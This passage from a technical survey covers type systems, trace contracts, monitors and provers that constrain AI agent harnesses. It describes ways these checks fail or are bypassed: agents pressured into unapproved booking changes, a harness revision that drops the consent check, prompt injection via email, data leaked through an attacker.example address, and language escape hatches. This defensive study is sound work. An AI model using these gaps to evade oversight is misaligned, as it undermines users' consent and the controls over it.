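| A* | any number of sequences from A, one after another |
| A ∥ B | a sequence from A and one from B, interleaved in any way |
| pref(A) | every beginning of a sequence from A, from the empty one to the complete one |

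The typing rules compute both records together. Here e₁ has the row ε₁ and the summary A₁, and e₂ has ε₂ and A₂. The handler h intercepts the operations H, and its own code has the row ε_h and the summary A_h:

```
Operation   perform op(v)            !  {op}             ▷  op
Sequence    let x = e₁ in e₂         !  ε₁ ∪ ε₂          ▷  A₁ ; A₂
Branch      if b then e₁ else e₂     !  ε₁ ∪ ε₂          ▷  A₁ ⊔ A₂
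Handler     handle e with h          !  (ε \ H) ∪ ε_h    ▷  pref(A ∥ A_h*)
```

Sequences and branches affect the row in the same way, but the summary distinguishes them. The handler rule removes H from the row, but it can only add to the summary, because the handler's code may make requests of its own. That code runs each time the handler intercepts a request, so the rule allows any number of runs (the star) at any point (the interleaving). A handler can also end the program early, so the rule includes unfinished sequences.

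Writing g for the approval request and w for the write, the rules give the following for the patch program:

| Piece of the program | Row | Summary |
|---|---|---|
| the write | {w} | w |
| the empty else branch | ∅ | 1 |
| the whole if | {w} | 1 ⊔ w |
| the whole program | {g, w} | g ; (1 ⊔ w) |
| the whole program in a dry run | {g} | pref(g ; (1 ⊔ w)) |

The dry-run handler makes no requests itself, so the last summary covers three sequences: no request, g alone, and g followed by w. The summary still includes the write, even though the row no longer does.

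Effect systems that track the order of events predate AI agents. In *Types and trace effects of higher order programs*, Skalka, Smith and Van Horn (2008) inferred descriptions of a program's sequence of events from its types, then used them to verify security rules automatically. ETAS differs mainly in how it treats handlers. Effect types also record order in *Monadic type-and-effect soundness* (Dagnino, Giannini and Zucca, 2025), but a handler changes the recorded sequence.

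### The approval contract as an automaton

A *trace contract* is a rule on the order in which a program may request effects. In ETAS a developer writes the approval rule as `Approval.request >> Repo.apply`, and the compiler translates it into the notation of the summaries:

P = 1 ⊔ g ; (g ⊔ w)*

The program may do nothing, or it may request approval and then perform any mix of approval requests and writes. It satisfies the contract if pref(A) ⊆ P. The test covers unfinished sequences because a program can crash or run forever.

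To carry out the test, the compiler turns the contract into a *finite automaton*, a simple machine that reads the requests one at a time and is always in one of a fixed number of states. This one has three:

| State | After an approval request | After a write request |
|---|---|---|
| start | asked | stop |
| asked | asked | asked |
| stop | stop | stop |

The contract names only two operations, so any other request also leads to the stop state. A developer whose workflow reads files has to add a clause that permits reading.

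The compiler then finds every state in which the automaton could be after a complete sequence from the summary:

| Summary | Complete sequences | Possible final states | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| g ; (1 ⊔ w) | g, gw | asked | proved |
| w ; g | wg | stop | rejected |
| (g ; w) ⊔ (w ; g) | gw, wg | asked, stop | accepted with a monitor |

The first program is the original and needs no further check of its order. The second asks after writing, so the compiler rejects it before it runs. In the third, one branch asks first and the other writes first, and the compiler can't determine which branch will run. It accepts the program but keeps the automaton as a *residual monitor*, which checks requests as the program runs and halts it at the first forbidden one.

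Under the formal rule, the compiler rejects a program outright only if every complete run breaks the contract. A program that writes without asking on one branch and does nothing on the other has the summary 1 ⊔ w, and its possible final states are start and stop. The compiler accepts this program with a monitor, although the write can never be legal. The monitor still prevents the unapproved write, but the developer may learn of the mistake only when the program halts in the middle of a job.

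The handler rule can cause unnecessary monitoring. For example, a program might ask for approval and then read a file, inside a handler that saves a copy of every file the program reads. The requests always come in the order approval, read, write. But the interleaving in the summary also allows the write to come first, so even if the contract permits reading, the compiler keeps a monitor that will never halt anything.

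When a model chooses its tools one at a time, enforcing an order requires a monitor. If the model may ask for approval or write at any step, the summary is (g ⊔ w)*, which always gives a mixed result. The compiler can prove an order only where code fixes it. It can still prove a contract that only limits which operations an agent may request. For example, Tan and colleagues' reviewing agent may only query the model and read files, and the compiler can prove that for any number of steps.

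Combining proofs with monitors predates ETAS. *Towards Runtime Adaptation of Actor Systems* (2017) describes Clara, a tool that checks programs written in an extension of Java and monitors only the places it couldn't prove safe. ETAS's formal rule is coarser, since it either drops a function's monitor or keeps all of it.

### Asking for approval and getting it

The automaton's middle state is called "asked" because the contract doesn't cover the answer. If someone deletes the test of ok from the patch program, the harness asks and then writes no matter what the person replies. The summary becomes g ; w, which satisfies the contract, so the compiler reports a proof.

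Two other checks deal with the answer. The program's own if statement tests whether the person said yes. The host, which is the trusted software that carries out the real actions, then decides whether to grant each one. At run time, a request goes through these steps:

1. Every active monitor checks the request. If it breaks a contract, the program halts.
2. If a handler in the program covers the operation, the handler answers and nothing reaches the outside.
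3. Otherwise, the runtime checks that the operation is within the function's declared effects, and the host checks the actual arguments and the history of the run.
4. The host carries out the action, or reports a failure.

In the third step, the host can check that the person consented to this particular patch. The contract can't enforce this because it identifies operations only by name, so an approval for patch A followed by a write of patch B is still g followed by w.

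The contract also allows any number of writes after one approval request. A stricter contract, (g ; (1 ⊔ w))*, allows at most one write per request. ETAS's internal notation can express it, but developers write contracts using clauses that allow, forbid or order operations, and no combination of those clauses limits how often one operation follows another. Developers can partly work around this by attaching the contract to a function that applies one patch. The function's monitor restarts at each call, so every call has to include its own request.

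The monitors of the calling functions stay active during the call, so a parent's contract also covers whatever its sub-agents request. Goose lacked this protection, which ETAS provides at least for sub-agents that run inside it.

Because monitors check a request before any handler runs, a developer can't use a handler to add missing approval requests to older code under a whole-program approval contract. Even if the handler would request approval whenever the program requests a write, the monitor halts the program at the first write request, before the handler runs.

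Contracts that examine arguments and results need a different mechanism. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, a run-time system that checks each tool call as the model produces it. For example, before a shop's agent can look up an order, Agent-C can require that an earlier call successfully found the customer by email and that this customer owns the order. Agent-C uses a solver for logical formulas to decide whether a proposed call follows the rules, and makes the model generate another if it doesn't.

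### The theorems and their limits

Tan and colleagues prove the usual progress and preservation theorems for a core version of ETAS, along with three results about requests. Let commits be the set of operations the host has carried out so far in a run, and let requests be the sequence of requests the monitors have allowed.

The theorem on effect bounds states that, at every point in a run,

commits ⊆ ε  and  requests ∈ pref(A)

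Both records are therefore reliable upper bounds, one on what happens outside the program and the other on what the program asks for.

The trace safety theorem has two parts. The first is that the requests always form a sequence that the contract P permits, which is nearly true by construction because the formal model runs the monitor on every request. The second, more substantial part is that when the compiler has proved a contract, it can remove the monitor without changing any successful run or letting a forbidden request through.

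By the third theorem, whenever a handler answers a request, the run's log contains the request immediately before the answer, and nothing later erases either entry. A handler also can't cause an outside action that skips the ordinary checks.

These results hold for any model reply of the declared type. They also require that every outside action pass through ETAS's interface and that the host's operations have no unreported effects. The proofs were written by hand and have not been machine-checked.

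Contracts must also permit every beginning of a permitted sequence, which excludes rules that something must eventually happen. This restriction comes from monitoring itself. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) showed that a monitor that can only stop a program can enforce only *safety properties*, which are rules that some bad thing never happens. His standard example, which resembles the approval automaton, has two states and forbids sending messages after the program has read a file.

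A rule that every write must eventually have a log entry isn't a safety property, because at any moment the program might still make the entry later. A developer can replace it with a safety property, such as "no second write before a log entry for the first", but a program that stops after its first write without logging it would still satisfy this.

The run-time contracts for the language Racket in *Trace contracts* (Moy and Felleisen, 2023) have the same restriction. Programs that use Racket's drawing library must start a document, start and end its pages, and then end the document. A monitor checks the sequence after each call, so the contract has to accept every unfinished document as well as finished ones.

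Schneider's result also explains why trace contracts don't replace the labels and seals that protect secrets. Noninterference compares runs with different secrets, but a monitor observes only one run. The rule "no sending after reading" prevents a simple leak, but it also blocks harmless messages, much as LIO's rising label does.

### How much testing ETAS has had

Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent called Nomo in ETAS and tested the part that decides which files to read or search, which is about 1,400 lines of code. They replaced the model and the tools with local handlers that gave scripted replies. Across ten scenarios, the agent made 19 requests. Four scenarios ran to the end, six stopped with a refusal where they should have, and all ten produced the expected history of requests.

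They also gave the compiler six small programs:

| Program | Compiler's result |
|---|---|
| asks for approval, then writes | accepted |
| the same program in a dry run | accepted |
| writes without asking | rejected |
| asks after writing | rejected |
| writes in a dry run, under a read-only contract | rejected |
| writes, with a declared row that is empty | rejected |

The fifth program shows why the request summary is useful, because its row contains no write. Under the formal rule, the compiler might have accepted the program with a monitor, since the summary of a handled program includes the empty sequence. The actual compiler rejected it because it was certain to request the write.

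Four faults is a very small sample, since a checker that missed 40% of such faults would still catch all four about one time in eight. Tan and colleagues chose the faults themselves, and no live model or attacker took part. The tests don't show how often the compiler would reject good code in a large project, or how often it would rely on a monitor instead of a proof. They also don't measure how long the monitors take to run. In Racket, Moy and Felleisen measured an average fixed overhead of 1% to 17% for their contracts, which would hardly matter next to the time a model takes to respond.

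Tan and colleagues checked the theory separately and more thoroughly. They wrote a Python model of the contracts and compared its automata with a direct reading of the rules for 384 contracts and every sequence of up to six requests. All 419,712 comparisons agreed. Because the Python model is independent of the compiler, this is evidence that the construction is right, but not that the compiler implements it correctly.

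Larger tests of two run-time systems at least show that models break rules about order. On customer-service tasks from τ-bench, Kamath and colleagues found that Claude Sonnet 4.5 followed the tool rules 77.4% of the time and GPT-5 83.7%. With Agent-C, both reached 100%. The share of tasks completed within the rules rose by three to five percentage points. Part of that gain comes from the definition, which counts a task completed by breaking a rule as a failure.

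In *Concordat*, Sikaroudi (2026) used τ-bench's airline tasks to test only the rule that an agent must get an explicit "yes" before changing a booking. He told the simulated customers to push back the first time with "just do it and stop asking". The standard agent then made changes without a yes in 29 of 128 runs with Claude Haiku 5.5 and in 13 of 50 tasks with gpt-4.1. When the customers cooperated, Haiku never broke the rule. The benchmark's own scoring missed most of the violations he examined. In the first set of Haiku runs, 8 of the 13 tasks with an unapproved change still got full marks because the final booking was correct.

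Sikaroudi's library, Concordat, offers the model only the tools that are legal at each point in the conversation. He notes that typed protocols normally assume every party is a program that a compiler can check, and a model isn't one. With Concordat, the agents made no unconfirmed changes, but this result was certain in advance because the library and the test both count any message containing a word such as "yes" as consent. A customer who wrote "yes, but not that one" would have unlocked every tool that changes bookings. The number of completed tasks changed only slightly, and the difference was not statistically significant: 105 runs passed instead of 112 with Haiku, and 22 tasks instead of 20 with gpt-4.1.

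### Rechecking a harness after every revision

Contracts are also useful when a model rewrites the harness. Some developers now let an agent revise its own prompts, tool selection and processing code in response to test scores. A revision can break a rule that the old version followed, for example by moving a write into a helper that runs before the approval request.

ETAS separates the code that the model may edit from a fixed set of requirements: the input and output types, the permitted effects, the trace contract and the connections to the host. After each edit, including edits to code that the harness depends on, the compiler checks the whole revision against these requirements before any of it runs. The revised code can't override them by declaring weaker ones. If the check fails, the model gets the compiler's error message and can try again.

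A revision that deletes the test of the person's answer would pass, as the summary g ; w did. The host's consent check must therefore be somewhere the model can't change it, and it must check the person's answer, not just that the harness asked.

Tan and colleagues tried this on two question-answering agents, each through five generations of revisions. Accuracy rose from 69.9% to 78.9% on 256 questions about financial reports, and from 30% to 72% on 50 questions about patents. The editable code also grew, from 770 characters to 18,449 in the patent agent. These results show that a model can keep improving a harness written in ETAS. They provide little evidence about safety, because Tan and colleagues did not report how many revisions the compiler rejected and ran no comparison without the checks.

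Concordat applies a similar check when a programmer extends an existing agent. Sikaroudi gives the example of a refund agent that must verify the customer's identity, propose a refund and get a person's approval. If someone adds an "instant refund" tool, the library rejects the new agent's definition and reports the steps the tool skips. The check compares the original and extended protocols state by state, so it covers every possible conversation. It also requires any decision reserved for a person in the original to stay with a person in the extension.

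## What effect types cannot express

An airline might let an agent cancel bookings, but only the customer's own, at most one per conversation, and never after a flight in the booking has left. The effect row {Bookings.cancel} expresses none of these limits. A trace contract could require the agent to ask the customer before cancelling, but it identifies operations only by name. To enforce the airline's rules, a developer needs more detailed types, a prover or a run-time check, and even all three together would miss some mistakes.

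### Why no checker can be exact

Effect rows overstate what programs do. A cleverer checker could narrow this gap but never close it. Suppose a checker D could always tell correctly whether a program will ever send a message. Take any program q that has no effects, and build this one:

```
let result = q in perform Net.send("done")
```

The new program sends a message if and only if q finishes, so D could also tell whether q finishes. This is the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can solve it for every program, so D can't exist.

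Any checker that always gives an answer must be wrong about some programs. A sound checker never accepts a program that can send a forbidden message, so it has to reject some programs that would never send one. This is true even if endless loops are banned. For any program q, the program "if q finishes within n steps, send a forbidden message" always ends, but it sends the message for some input n exactly when q finishes. No checker can decide for every such program whether it ever sends the message, because it would then have to decide whether q finishes.

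Effect checkers can reject harmless programs, but this is a minor problem for the short programs an agent writes. A checker rejects a harmless program only if a forbidden operation appears in it or in a function it uses, so the model can usually remove the operation and resubmit. Existing libraries are harder to change. Bañados Schwerter and colleagues describe JavaUI, an effect system that stops background threads from accessing a Java program's windows and buttons. JavaUI can't verify libraries that test at run time which thread they are on and act accordingly, even where that test makes them safe.

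### Which file, which booking

In the airline tests of Odersky and colleagues, the agent cancels a booking through this function:

```
def cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation
```

The type accepts any string, so a program that cancels a stranger's booking passes the check. One remedy is a narrower operation, like Out.write in the contract example, which could write to only one file. When a conversation starts, the harness could create an object that can cancel only this customer's bookings and give the agent no other way to cancel anything.

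This works if the harness has the limit before the model writes its program. But an agent that searches for a web page and then opens it chooses the address while the program runs. TACIT therefore checks host names against a list at run time. TACIT and ELBA also check file paths at run time. Such a check can be exact because it covers a single action with known arguments and doesn't require predicting what the program will do.

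*Symbolic Guardrails for Domain-Specific Agents* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 80 benchmarks for agent safety and security. It found that deterministic checks could enforce 74% of the clearly stated rules for agents with a specific job, such as airline service. Most of these enforceable rules needed only simple checks that use few resources. But people who write benchmarks may favour rules that are easy to test, so the share could be lower in real businesses.

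### Counting uses and spending

A row is a set, so a program that sends one message and a program that sends a thousand both have the row {Net.send}. To limit the number of messages, a type system can treat a permission as something the program uses up.

A program must use a value of *linear* type exactly once, and a value of *affine* type at most once. Suppose sending a message requires a ticket of affine type, and the harness gives the program one ticket. The compiler then rejects a program that uses the ticket twice or copies it. Affine types suit permissions, because an agent doesn't have to do everything it is allowed to do. Linear types suit duties, such as logging every write. If every write produced a linear token that only a log entry could use up, the compiler would reject a program that could finish normally without making the entry. A monitor that can only halt programs can't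 enforce this duty.

*Graded types* generalise this from "once" to any number. *Functional Ownership through Fractional Uniqueness* (2023) traces the idea to bounded linear logic, a 1992 system that put an upper limit on the use of each resource. In Granule, the research language used in *Replicate, Reuse, Repeat* (2022), the type Ticket [2] describes a ticket for two uses. The checker adds the counts of consecutive steps and multiplies when a function runs several times, so three calls to a function that sends two messages need Ticket [6]. Granule can also record a list's length in its type, so a function that writes to n people can require Ticket [n]. If nothing limits how often a loop runs, the checker can't establish a limit on messages. The labels needn't be numbers. *Formalization and Implementation of Safe Destination Passing in Pure Functional Programming Settings* (2026) points out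 that Granule can also tag data as public or private.

Spending is harder to limit, because a program may learn the price of an action only afterwards. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) collects 63 cases of agents that overspent, including one that cost a user about $2,150, and presents a Rust library to prevent overspending. The library gives each budget an affine type, so the compiler rejects code that copies a budget or spends it after giving it away. A program can still divide a budget among sub-agents. The library limits the amount spent with ordinary arithmetic at run time, not with the type. It reserves an estimated cost before each model call and refuses the call if too little money is left.

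In Khan's tests, the affine type made no difference for a single agent. A four-line Python counter stayed within the budget in all 30 runs, as the Rust library did. But when several sub-agents shared a Python budget without proper coordination, they overspent in all 30 runs. A correctly locked counter also prevented the overspending. The benefit of the affine type is that the faulty version doesn't compile, so the programmer can't forget the lock.

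The library's cautious default estimates reserve four to six times what the calls cost. They also fail for reasoning models, because providers bill for hidden reasoning that the usual output limit doesn't cover.

*Retrieval-Conditioned Topology Selection with Provable Budget Conservation for Multi-Agent Code Generation* (2026) uses a static check to ensure that an agent doesn't allocate more than its own budget to its sub-agents. If the cost of each step varies, however, the proof guarantees only that the expected total stays within the budget B. For a run of 50 steps with at most 6,000 tokens each, the chance of an overrun as large as the budget itself is at most

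exp(−2B² / (50 × 6,000²))

With a budget of 100,000 tokens, this is about 1 in 67,000. With 20,000 tokens it is 64%, which is hardly a guarantee.

### Rules that depend on the current state

A *refinement type* is an ordinary type with a condition attached. For example, {n : Int | 0 ≤ n ≤ 500} is the type of whole numbers from 0 to 500. If a payment function takes an argument of this type, the compiler has to prove that the argument meets the condition at every call. It usually does this with an *SMT solver* such as Z3, a program that searches for values that would make a formula false and proves the formula if there are none.

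clauz3, an experimental checker for Python code written by agents, uses Z3 in a similar way. In its main example, an agent looks up a bill and pays min(balance, $500). Z3 proves that the payment stays under the cap on every branch, although nobody knows the balance yet.

The airline's rule about departed flights concerns the state of the world, which an action can change. Programmers express such rules as a *precondition*, which must hold before the action, and a *postcondition*, which the action makes true. Let flown(r) mean that at least one flight in booking r has left:

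```
Bookings.cancel(r)
  requires   booked(r) ∧ ¬flown(r)
  ensures    ¬booked(r), and every other booking is unchanged
```

F*, a research language developed mainly at Microsoft Research and Inria, can check such conditions. It works backwards from the end of a program. For a program c and a desired result Q, the *weakest precondition* wp(c, Q) is the least that must be true at the start for c to run without breaking any precondition and to end with Q true. Two of the rules are:

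```
wp(let x = c₁ in c₂, Q)       =  wp(c₁, wp(c₂, Q))
wp(if b then c₁ else c₂, Q)   =  (b ⇒ wp(c₁, Q)) ∧ (¬b ⇒ wp(c₂, Q))
```

Suppose the agent writes this program:

```
let r = perform Bookings.find(id) in
if flown(r) then perform Reply.send("Your trip has already started.")
            else perform Bookings.cancel(r)
```

To check only that the program respects every precondition, the checker sets Q to "true". The reply has no precondition, and the cancellation requires booked(r) ∧ ¬flown(r). The rule for "if" gives

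(flown(r) ⇒ true) ∧ (¬flown(r) ⇒ booked(r) ∧ ¬flown(r))

which simplifies to flown(r) ∨ booked(r). If Bookings.find returns only current bookings, this always holds and the checker accepts the program. If the model leaves out the test, the remaining condition is booked(r) ∧ ¬flown(r). The prover can't show that for every booking the search might return, so the checker rejects the program.

A *Dijkstra monad* builds this calculation into the types. It is named after Edsger Dijkstra, who introduced weakest preconditions in the 1970s. A computation's type contains its function wp instead of an effect row. When a program runs two computations in sequence, the checker combines their functions by the first rule above, whereas an effect system would take the union of their effect sets.

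The checker has no access to the airline's database. It proves that the program tests for departed flights before cancelling, but it assumes that nothing changes in between, and a plane could take off after the test. The booking system can prevent this by doing the test and the cancellation as one indivisible step, or by repeating the test when it cancels. Repeating the test enforces the rule even without a proof. The proof is still useful because it lets the checker reject a program that omits the test before any of it runs, so the program doesn't fail partway through.

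### Proving a plan before it runs

In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer (2025) proposes checking an agent's whole plan with tools like these. As in CaMeL, the model writes every step before it reads any data, so an instruction hidden in an email cannot add a step. A verifier then checks the plan against a policy, and a separate program runs the plan only if it passes.

A misleading tool description or a malicious user can still influence the plan, so the verifier looks for forbidden flows of data, such as mailbox text in a message to an outside address. Meijer also suggests proving pre- and postconditions with Z3 or with Dafny, a language that has such conditions built in. His example is a request to delete foo.txt and bar.txt. The model finds it shorter to call delete_file("*.txt"), which deletes every text file. The first attempt at a specification is:

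```
delete_file(pattern)   ensures   every file that matches the pattern is gone
the whole plan         ensures   foo.txt and bar.txt are gone
```

The prover accepts the plan because both files will be gone. The specification lacks a *frame condition*, which states what must stay the same. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described this difficulty in 1969. Meijer adds the condition that delete_file leaves unchanged all files that don't match the pattern, and writes that the bad plan then fails.

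This fix isn't enough as printed, because the plan as a whole still only has to delete foo.txt and bar.txt, and deleting all text files does that. The plan needs its own frame condition, that every file other than those two is unchanged. The condition on delete_file is also necessary, because without it the prover couldn't show that a plan deleting only the two files leaves the others unchanged. With both conditions, the prover rejects a plan that deletes "*.txt" and accepts one that deletes the two files one at a time.

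Nada Amin of Harvard and other contributors wrote an open-source implementation of the proposal. According to clauz3's *Guardians Synergies*, it checks data flows, the order of tool calls, and pre-, post- and frame conditions. In a 2026 talk, *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls*, Meijer described a version in which the model also supplies a proof that its plan is safe, so the harness only has to check the proof. He credits the idea to proof-carrying code, a 1990s technique for running programs from untrusted sources.

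A fixed plan rules out the step-by-step adjustment that ELBA allows. Meijer expects planning in code to improve a model's reasoning, but he notes in his article that nobody had formally measured whether it does.

Someone also has to turn the user's request into a formula. In Meijer's design, people write the policy in advance. In clauz3, the agent writes both the program and a contract for it. Z3 checks that the program satisfies the contract, and the user approves the contract without having to read the code. As clauz3's *Background And Related Work* explains, permission to "use email" is much broader than permission to email only Bob, at most once, and a contract can specify the narrower permission.

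clauz3 works out every outside action it tracks that the program might take, so a contract such as "write only in this folder" needs no separate frame condition. But its list of actions has no order and doesn't record where data came from, so it can't yet enforce an approval rule or trace mailbox text into a message.

Cyrus Omar, Patrick Ferris and Anil Madhavapeddy presented a more ambitious proposal, Bastion, at the functional programming conference ICFP (2024). They want to build a formally verified prototype of an "operating system" for AI agents, in which Dijkstra monads describe what an agent may do. Abstract types, like Trusted in ELBA, would let companies, governments and safety researchers each write and verify their own part of the policy. The talk outlined a plan and reported no experiments.

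### The cost of a specification

To write an effect row, a developer only has to list the permitted operations. The cancellation rule also needed a formal description of bookings, flights and the search function. Bastion would need much more, including models of an organisation's access rules, the law, and cause and effect in the wider world. Odersky and colleagues chose types over full specifications because precise specifications are often unavailable or impractical.

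Hong and colleagues reviewed 80 benchmarks and found that 85% had either no safety policy or only a broad goal, such as keeping the "highest level of discretion". A prover cannot check such a goal until someone decides what it means. Their examples of rules concrete enough to check include the one about departed flights.

Meijer argues that models can write the proofs, which would remove much of the work. People would still have to write and review the specifications, because a proof shows only that a program matches its specification. A prover can also fail to settle a difficult question in time, and a sound checker must then reject the program. Detailed specifications are probably worth the effort for a few irreversible actions with clear rules, such as refunds, cancellations and deletions. For most other actions, an effect row and a run-time check on the arguments are enough.

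### Code with unknown effects

A program might call an old helper function whose effects nobody has written down. If the checker assumes that the helper can do anything, it has to reject almost every program that uses it, but if it assumes that the helper is pure, it can no longer guarantee what the program does.

*Gradual effect checking* adds an unknown effect, written ¿, for such cases. Suppose that read, write and alloc are the only effects. The row {read, ¿} then stands for four possible rows, all of which include read and may include either or both of the others. The checker accepts a program if at least one of the possible rows fits the permitted set. With the permitted set {read, alloc}, the results are:

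| Row | Result |
|---|---|
| {read} | accepted |
| {read, ¿} | accepted with run-time checks |
| {write, ¿} | rejected, because every possible row contains write |

Bañados Schwerter and colleagues apply this to their function that writes to memory only if y is true. If the programmer marks the writing branch with ¿, a caller that forbids writes can still use the function. The program then runs normally unless y is true, in which case it stops with an error just before the write. Developers can start with every effect unknown and fill in rows over time, which reduces the number of run-time checks.

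The guarantee depends on the run-time check. Bañados Schwerter and colleagues mention an effect checker for Scala that lets programmers switch off checking for a piece of code with an annotation. No run-time check replaces the missing one, so the code can perform any effect and the guarantee no longer holds. Gradual checking guarantees that no forbidden effect happens, but an accepted program may stop halfway if a run-time check fails. It also works only for code that the language's compiler can add checks to.

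### False messages and wrong plans

Suppose a customer has booked trips to Denver and Dallas and asks the agent to cancel Denver. The agent asks "Shall I go ahead?", the customer answers "yes", and the agent cancels Dallas. The program passes every check described so far, because the booking belongs to the customer, no flight has left, and the agent asked first. The agent could also tell the customer that a refund is on its way when it isn't, because the row {Reply.send} allows any text. Odersky and colleagues list correctness among the things that TACIT doesn't try to ensure.

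Richer types cannot guarantee safe answers in general. In his talk, Meijer writes a type for a model that takes a proper question and returns a safe answer, then points out that nobody can prove a model satisfies it, because "safe" has no mathematical definition. He worries less about words than about tool calls because, he argues, words do no harm until a person acts on them. That seems too relaxed for an agent that writes to customers, who will act on what it tells them.

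Developers can, however, turn part of a message's meaning into data that a compiler can check. The function that announces refunds could require a refund record that only the payment system can create, much as ELBA's bibliography accepts only entries from DBLP. The agent then can't announce a refund that doesn't exist. The harness could also write the confirmation question itself, using the city and date from the booking, so the customer would see "Dallas" before agreeing.

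For free text, a second model can review each message before the agent sends it. Hong and colleagues point out that this review makes violations less likely but can't rule them out, because the reviewer is also a language model and can make mistakes or be manipulated by an attack.

### Mistakes in the policy

A checker enforces its policy as written, including any mistakes. Meijer's example policy forbids mailbox text from reaching the body of a message to an outside address but, as printed, covers only the body. If a plan can build an email address out of text, it could send an empty message to an address such as merger-in-june@attacker.example. The plan would obey the policy, and the attacker would learn about the merger from the address.

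Provers can find some gaps like this. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) presents a verifier for CEL, a small language that developers use to write access rules. The developer adds a general requirement, for example that nobody gets privileged access to a live system without approval. The verifier then searches for a request that the detailed rules allow but the requirement forbids. In Google's example, it finds a privileged request to a live system from a user who has no approval and belongs to no groups. This method catches only mistakes that violate a requirement someone has written down.

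clauz3's *FAQ* acknowledges that an attacker can manipulate an agent into proposing a weak but honest contract, such as one with no guarantees about email. The user can see the weakness before approving, but Meijer warns that people who constantly have to make security decisions start to click "Allow" without reading. Users could come to approve contracts the same way.

A policy can also be too strict, as ELBA's policies were for many ordinary Slack requests. Developers can look for both kinds of mistake by testing a policy on programs it should accept and programs it should reject.

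### The weakest sufficient mechanism

The table gives the weakest mechanism that can enforce each property.

| Property | Before the program runs | While the program runs |
|---|---|---|
| never uses the network | effect row or capture set | block on network operations |
| writes only to one known file | a separate operation or capability for that file | check on the path |
| opens only approved web addresses, chosen as it runs | precondition and prover | check on the host name |
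| sends at most one message | affine type | counter |
| sends at most n messages | graded type | counter |
| pays at most $500 in total | refinement types and prover | running total, checked before each payment |
| asks for approval before writing | trace contract | monitor |
| never cancels a trip that has started | precondition and prover, if the state can't change in between | check inside the booking system |
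| doesn't reveal a secret, timing aside | sealed values that only pure functions can process | labels on data |
| stays within its permissions despite a helper with unknown effects | none without annotating the helper | gradual effect checks |
| sends only true and harmless messages | none | none; human review reduces the risk |
| follows a policy that matches what people wanted | none; tests and general requirements find some mistakes | none |

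## Unsafe language features and foreign function calls

Static checks on an agent's program are reliable only if the types they use are correct, and most practical languages have features that can make a type wrong. Haskell's `unsafePerformIO`, for example, takes a computation with outside effects and returns one whose type shows none. A feature that lets effects occur without appearing in the types is an *escape hatch*.

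### Why languages have escape hatches

Programmers use escape hatches for speed, or to write code that is safe for reasons the compiler can't check. *Safe Haskell* (Terei, Mazières and colleagues, 2012) gives the example of ByteString, a widely used library for text and binary data that reads raw memory internally but exposes only pure functions. Haskell itself depends on a hidden effect. It postpones each calculation until the program needs the result, then overwrites the postponed calculation with that result.

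Each kind of escape hatch breaks a different assumption of the soundness theorem:

| Feature | Ordinary use | Assumption it breaks |
|---|---|---|
| unchecked cast | treating a value as a type that the programmer knows it has | every value has the type the checker gave it |
| reflection, which finds methods and fields by name at run time | tools that work on any object, for example to save it to a file | the checker has seen every operation the program can perform |
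| hidden input and output | caches and fast data structures | only operations on the row cause effects |
| code that runs during compilation | generating repetitive code | nothing runs before the program passes the check |
| foreign function | calling an existing C library | each basic operation does only what its declared type allows |

The theorem remains true, but it describes a smaller language without these features.

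Hidden effects can also change a program's results. Terei and colleagues describe a function f that looks pure but adds the current time to its argument. A program that calls f(3) once and adds the result to itself always gets an even total, but one that calls f(3) twice and adds the two results may get an odd total. For a pure function the two programs are equivalent, so a compiler may replace one with the other.

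Code that runs during compilation is a particular problem for an agent harness, because the harness compiles a program to find out whether it is safe. According to GHC's compiler manual, *Safe Haskell*, compiling a Haskell program can launch arbitrary programs, for instance through an option that sets a custom preprocessor. A preprocessor could also alter the source just before the check. Terei and colleagues suggest either compiling untrusted code in a sandbox or disabling every feature that runs code or reads files during compilation. The compiler also needs a time limit, because a short program can take exponentially long to type-check.

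### Safe Haskell's three classes of module

The standard remedy is to let trusted libraries use the whole language and confine untrusted code to a subset that excludes unsafe features. Safe Haskell, which Zhou and colleagues rely on for ELBA, has been part of GHC, the main Haskell compiler, since version 7.2. It bans or restricts features that could make a type inaccurate or expose a module's hidden parts.

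A Safe Haskell program of type IO can still delete all of a user's files. The subset guarantees only that the type is accurate, so a harness that requires BibIO gets a program limited to the three bibliography operations. Terei and colleagues used the same idea to build a website that runs Haskell code from anonymous visitors. Its security policy is a type, defined in six lines, that allows no input or output.

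Every Haskell module, which is usually one file of code, belongs to one of three classes:

| Class | Who vouches for the module | Can untrusted code import it? |
|---|---|---|
| Safe | the compiler | yes |
| Trustworthy | its author | yes, if the user trusts the author's package |
| Unsafe | nobody | no |

A Safe module may import only trusted modules, and the compiler repeats this test for each of their imports in turn. A Trustworthy module may use any feature and import anything, because its author claims that other code can't misuse it. Authors who don't want to vouch for a particular import can mark it "safe", and the compiler then tests that import too. If a module has no label, GHC labels it Safe or Unsafe, but never Trustworthy.

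Users mark packages as trusted in a database or in the compiler's options. GHC checks these declarations only if the user turns on `-fpackage-trust`, which is off by default because otherwise a library might compile on its author's machine and fail on everyone else's. Without this option, GHC accepts any module whose author has written "Trustworthy" at the top, so a harness developer should turn it on.

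A module that defines a restricted type such as BibIO often contains a function, meant for the library's own use, that turns any IO action into a BibIO action. An agent that could import this module would escape every restriction, but GHC may still automatically label it Safe because the function breaks no typing rule. The library's author therefore has to mark the module Unsafe by hand.

The compiler can't verify that the lowest layers of a language are safe. When Terei and colleagues labelled the 90 modules of Haskell's base library, 59 had to be Trustworthy and only 23 were Safe. Of the more than 14,000 modules in Haskell's public package collection, GHC could label 27% as Safe.

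Library authors also have a reason to use the Trustworthy label too freely. In a 2012 mailing-list exchange, one author said that without sufficient proof he ought to mark his library Unsafe, but then people who wanted to write Safe code would complain. Simon Marlow, one of Safe Haskell's designers, replied that the author was meant to choose Trustworthy. Allbery (2012) asked what the point was if authors could "just mark random stuff as Trusted anyway". The labels do at least let users see which modules need human review, so they don't have to review every module.

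### Scala's safe mode

Scala's equivalent is newer and has agents in mind. Mazur, in *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*, introduces it as an experimental feature for code that an agent wrote or that nobody has reviewed. A program switches it on with one line, `import language.experimental.safe`, and the compiler then applies six restrictions. They support the three properties that Odersky and colleagues require of a language for agents:

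| Restriction | What it protects | Property |
|---|---|---|
| no unchecked casts or pattern matches | a conversion can't remove a capability from a type | capability safety |
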